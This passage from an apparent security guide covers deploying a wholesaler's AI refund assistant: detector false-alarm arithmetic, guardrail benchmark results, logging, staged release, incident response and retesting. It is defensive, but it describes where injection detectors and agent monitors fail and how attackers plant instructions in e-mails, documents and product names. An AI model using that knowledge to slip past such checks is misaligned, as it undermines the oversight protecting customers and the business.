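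Testing with typical questions is a poor guide to how the deployment will withstand an attacker, who looks for the rare question that works. Researchers have found that attackers who adapt to a published filter can generally get past it.

Permissions don't need to be sampled, because a script can compare the access list in the index with the one in the document store for all 40,000 documents and report every difference. The 300 questions then mainly test for problems the script can't detect, such as a search that skips the filter or an answer served from a cache.

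### How many alerts are real

A filter typically gives each message a score and blocks those that score above a threshold the wholesaler chooses. Suppose 100 of 100,000 messages are attacks, and the filter blocks 95% of attacks and 1% of harmless messages. It would block 95 attacks, miss five, and wrongly block 999 of the 99,900 harmless messages. Only 95 of the 1,094 blocked messages, or about 9%, would be attacks.

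Moving the threshold trades one error for the other. The first and last rows below use invented rates to illustrate this:

| Threshold | Detection | False alarm rate | Caught | Missed | False alarms | Alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Low | 99% | 5% | 99 | 1 | 4,995 | 2% |
| Medium | 95% | 1% | 95 | 5 | 999 | 9% |
| High | 80% | 0.1% | 80 | 20 | 100 | 44% |

At two minutes per alert, the low threshold creates about 170 hours of work, the medium one 36 and the high one six. The right choice depends on what happens to a blocked message. If it goes to an employee who would have approved the refund anyway, a false alarm does little harm. If the customer receives a refusal, the wholesaler could lose 999 honest customers to other sellers of glasses. The wholesaler can also tolerate more missed attacks because of the limits in its refund code.

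Published results show the same effect. Shire and Kim (2026), in *PIDS-Bench*, calculated that 89% of their most accurate detector's alerts would be real if one message in ten were an attack, but only 7% if one in 1,000 were. *StepShield* (2026) tested monitors that watch for agents overstepping their instructions. When 8.1% of cases were bad, 60% of the alerts from a language model acting as judge were real, compared with 9% from a monitor based on fixed patterns. If one case in 1,000 were bad, less than 2% of the judge's alerts would be real.

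Adjusting a detector's threshold can't always stop it from blocking too many harmless prompts. Shire and Kim tested three detectors on 872 harmless prompts from public collections, all on subjects such as security or system prompts. At the standard threshold, the most accurate detector blocked 31% of them. No threshold got any of the three to block fewer than 10% while keeping the overall accuracy that the researchers required. The most accurate detector also made errors with high confidence, giving scores of at least 0.9 to about a third of a larger set of harmless prompts.

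The researchers then retrained it with 419 harmless examples that resembled attacks. False alarms fell from 48% to 0.1% on similar hand-written prompts, but only from 31.4% to 31.0% on the prompts from public collections. A vendor's claim to have fixed false alarms may therefore not hold for the wholesaler's mail. The wholesaler's test set should include real e-mails in which customers ask staff to ignore an earlier message or change an instruction.

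### Independent evaluations of guardrails

*BELLS-O*, by Waibl, Michalak and Mariaccia (2026), is probably the broadest recent comparison, covering 33 systems from 17 developers. None of the three researchers works for a guardrail vendor. They measured detection, false alarms, delay and cost on the same data. Alibaba's Qwen3Guard detected 94.9% of harmful requests, with no false alarms and a delay of 0.19 seconds. The general-purpose model gpt-oss-120b did about as well but took 0.72 seconds.

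In tests on prompt injection, a small detector called PIGuard caught 92.1% of attacks with a false-alarm rate of 0.3%, while Lakera Guard, a commercial product, caught 95.6% with a false-alarm rate of 14.4%. Both took 0.21 seconds. In tests on jailbreaks, Lakera Guard wrongly flagged 81.9% of harmless requests, many of which the researchers had worded to resemble attacks.

Waibl and colleagues did not test agents or live traffic, and PIGuard does much worse on the text that agents read. In *Passing the Test You Trained On*, Liu (2026) ran 15 detectors on the results of tool calls in two simulated settings. One was AgentDojo, the benchmark researchers used to test CaMeL. The other was τ-bench, which simulates customer service for a retailer and an airline, and Liu planted instructions in its product names. Each detector's threshold allowed a false alarm rate of 1%.

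| Detector | Planted text in BIPIA's e-mails, tables and code | AgentDojo | τ-bench |
|---|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | 95.1% | 2.1% | 52.7% |
| Prismor | 4.0% | 72.2% | 15.2% |
| Sheltron | 57.2% | 20.1% | 95.2% |
| Prompt Guard 2 (86M) | 10.4% | 69.4% | 57.9% |
| Horizon-Labs | 37.7% | 82.2% | 100.0% |

Liu found 1,116 BIPIA inputs in PIGuard's published training data, which largely explains PIGuard's score in the first column. According to Liu, Mozilla.ai's *Can Open-Source Guardrails Really Protect AI Agents?* relied on BIPIA to conclude that PIGuard detects indirect injection effectively. Horizon-Labs trained its detector on text that looks like tool results, and Liu found none of the three benchmarks' attacks in the training sources searched. *Evaluating the Robustness of Large Language Model Safety Guardrails Against Adversarial Attacks* (2025) raises a similar suspicion about guardrail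 models more widely, after finding a 57.2% drop in performance on new prompts.

False alarms were more consistent across Liu's two agent benchmarks. At its default threshold, PIGuard flagged 29.5% of harmless AgentDojo results, including a routine confirmation of a password change. Agents read several results per task, so these flags would have stopped 60% of tasks. Even at a 1% false-alarm rate, an agent that reads ten results has almost a 10% chance of at least one false alarm, if the errors are independent.

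Results for NeMo Guardrails vary even more:

| Study | Test data | Attacks detected | False alarms | Delay |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Koutidis and colleagues | 200 attacks in security logs, 1,000 harmless log lines | 94.5% | 0.1% | 14.14 s (median) |
| Maiorano | 369 attacks and 111 harmless questions from simulated students | 100% | 16.2% | About 1.5 s |
| *AgentTrust* | Actions by software agents | Not comparable | 96.2% | Not comparable |

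The first row comes from *Constrained-Action AI Remediation for SIEM/XDR via a NeMo-Guardrails Proxy* (Koutidis, Kekatos and colleagues, 2026). Three of the four authors work for the security company Clone Systems. They ran everything on one Apple computer, and each message that passed needed three model calls in sequence. Without the rails, the same model detected 25% of attacks in a median of 0.31 seconds. With the rails in place, using a smaller model to choose which messages needed the full check cut the median delay to 0.18 seconds but lowered detection to 58%.

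*Evaluating Prompt Injection Defenses for Educational LLM Tutors* (Maiorano, 2026) compared the library with the author's own filter, which raised no false alarms and took 2.5 milliseconds but missed 46% of attacks. *AgentTrust* (2026), which also promotes its own tool, rewrote a NeMo Guardrails input check to judge agents' actions. The rewritten check blocked almost every safe action, including routine programming commands.

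These figures are compatible because NeMo Guardrails is a framework, and each team supplied its own model and prompt. The library therefore has no single error rate.

Two industry sources report similar problems. Unit 42, the research group of the security vendor Palo Alto Networks, found that guardrails on several platforms often mistook harmless code-review requests for threats. *Persona Guardrail* (2026), in which developers describe their own system, reports that the fastest model they considered took 81 milliseconds but approved only 49% to 67% of harmless requests. A larger model took 95 milliseconds and approved at least 99%.

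The wholesaler should choose two or three candidates and run them on several thousand of its own old e-mails and tool results, some with planted instructions. It should set each threshold on one half of the data and measure errors on the other half, because a threshold tested on the same data used to set it will look more accurate than it is.

### What to log

After release, the wholesaler needs a record of each request that lets an investigator reconstruct what happened. For the four broken glasses, the record might be:

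```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-01T09:14:22Z",
  "request": "r-81f3",
  "user": "marta.k",
  "agent": "refund-assistant/17",
  "message": "mail-90412",
  "documents": ["returns-policy@v12"],
  "tool_call": {"name": "refund", "order": 58213,
                "item": "GL-204", "quantity": 4},
  "authorisation": {"decision": "allow", "limit": "40.00",
                    "reason": "task limit"},
  "rails": {"jailbreak": "allow", "topic": "allow",
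            "content_safety": "allow"},
  "versions": {"model": "main-2026-11", "prompt": "31",
               "rails_config": "a94c", "guardrails": "0.25.0",
               "refund_code": "2.8"},
  "result": "paid",
  "text": "store-6620"
}
```

The number in the `agent` field identifies the copy of the assistant, and the `versions` field lets an engineer check whether a problem began with a change to the prompt. NVIDIA documents how to record which rails ran and how to follow a request through several programs with OpenTelemetry, a common standard for tracing. The wholesaler's application has to add the user and the authorisation decision to the record.

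The assistant must not be able to alter the log. The Australian Signals Directorate and its Five Eyes counterparts recommend giving agents no write access to logs and requiring a person to approve any request to delete log entries. A separate program should therefore write the log.

The record stores only a reference to the conversation text, in the `text` field. David C advises companies to log enough to identify suspicious activity, "potentially including full input and output". But the GDPR allows a company to keep only the personal data it needs, and only for as long as it needs it. A complete log of context windows would copy customers' letters and contract clauses into another store, along with any salary the assistant had wrongly retrieved.

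Most of that copying is unnecessary. The customer's e-mail is already in the mailbox and the policy in the document store, so identifiers and version numbers are enough to find them. The only new text is what employees type and what the model writes. The wholesaler can keep that text, with personal data masked, in a separate encrypted store. An investigator should need a second person's approval to open it.

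The wholesaler should keep the text of conversations long enough for someone to notice a problem. If the finance department reviews refunds monthly, deleting the text after 14 days would destroy the evidence for refunds from the start of the month. Forty-five days covers the month plus two weeks to investigate. The wholesaler can then delete the text automatically, except for conversations under investigation, and keep the short records for perhaps a year. Those records name employees and can be linked to customers, so they are personal data too. The privacy notices should give both retention periods.

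This arrangement works only if the mailbox and document store keep old versions for the same 45 days. The provider's logs are no substitute, because they don't contain the wholesaler's authorisation decisions and the wholesaler may not be able to search them. If engineers use a language model to search the stored text, that model should have no tools, because the text may contain planted instructions.

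### Releasing in stages

The release test can't cover everything customers write, so the wholesaler should give the assistant more freedom only as results from real use come in.

| Stage | What the assistant does | Condition for moving on |
|---|---|---|
| Two weeks | Proposes refunds, which employees don't see while they decide as before | The team can explain every difference between the two |
| One month | Prepares refunds, and an employee approves each one | Employees correct fewer than 1%, and no request gets past a limit |
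| One month | Issues refunds of up to €20 alone | A weekly sample shows no payment that breaks the policy |
| Afterwards | Issues refunds of up to €50 alone | The weekly sample continues |

At 400 refunds a day, the second stage produces about 8,000 decisions in 20 working days. If a particular fault appears in none of them, the upper bound on its rate is about 0.04%. Unlike the release test result, this figure is based on real customers. The team can check whether employees read what they approve by adding a few deliberately wrong test refunds each week. If employees approve those, the low correction rate is not evidence that the other refunds were correct.

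Some events should trigger an alert:

| Event | Immediate response |
|---|---|
| A marked dummy document appears among the retrieved passages | Disconnect the source it came from and call the engineer on duty |
| The tools refuse three calls in one conversation | Withdraw the tools from that conversation and pass it to an employee |
| Refused calls rise across many customers | Compare them with recent changes and look for shared wording |
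| A rail that normally blocks several messages a day blocks none | Send it a message that it should block |
| Automatic refunds reach 80% of the daily cap before noon | Have an employee check the last 20 |

The first alert should have hardly any false alarms, because no employee has a reason to ask about an invented depot. The second alert interrupts an attacker who is still refining an attack. It will also send an honest customer who mistypes an order number three times to an employee, which does little harm.

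### When something goes wrong

Suppose an alert shows that the assistant is refunding orders that nobody complained about. The person on duty should first disable the assistant in the login system and set the refund system to reject the assistant's existing tokens. The shutdown must not depend on the model, the guardrails or the engineer who built them. While the assistant is off, customers' e-mails go to employees, so the customer service team needs a plan to handle about 400 refunds a day by hand.

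Next, the team revokes any other credentials an attacker may have obtained, such as the key for the model provider or the account that builds the index. Issuing a new key is not enough if the old one still works. The team should also suspend automatic deletion of logs, which might otherwise erase evidence in the text store during the investigation.

Engineers can then use the log to find out how far the problem spread. If the cause was an instruction planted in an e-mail or document, they can search for every request that used it. The instruction may also remain in the index, a cached answer or the assistant's memory. Unless the team removes it from all of them, the restarted assistant may read it again.

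If personal data has leaked, the GDPR normally requires the wholesaler to notify the regulator within 72 hours of becoming aware of the breach, unless the leak is unlikely to put anyone at risk. The wholesaler may also have to tell the people affected. The incident plan should list contact details for the regulator, the bank and the model provider, and name the people authorised to shut the assistant down.

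The Five Eyes agencies recommend testing such plans and being able to return to an earlier working version. In a practice run, the wholesaler can shut down a trial copy without warning and record when the last payment goes out, when the first e-mail reaches an employee and when the previous version is restored. After a real incident, the assistant should restart at the stage where employees approve every refund.

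### Retesting after a change

A newer model can be worse at a particular job. In the jailbreak tests by Waibl and colleagues, GPT-5.4 raised fewer false alarms than GPT-5.2 but detected 86.4% of attacks, down from 90.5%. A company that uses a model as a judge could therefore weaken its filter by upgrading. The wholesaler should request an exact model version from the provider where it can, and test every new version.

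| Change | Tests to repeat |
|---|---|
| Main model or its instructions | Planted instructions, tool calls and a sample of ordinary requests |
| Guardrail model, prompt or threshold | Detection and false alarms on the wholesaler's own data, and outages |
| Roles, groups or folder permissions | Rank, marked documents and revocation |
| New document source | Marked documents in that source, and planted instructions if outsiders can write to it |
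| New or changed tool | Out-of-range values, planted instructions and combinations with existing tools |
| Version of NeMo Guardrails | At least one message that each rail should block, and outages |

Some changes come from outside the wholesaler, such as faults in a supplier's software. One such fault let Copilot summarise labelled e-mails for about four weeks. A script can use a warehouse account to ask the assistant for the marked documents every night, with one question for each of the 25 dummy files. The wholesaler would then learn of a similar fault in its own assistant the next morning.
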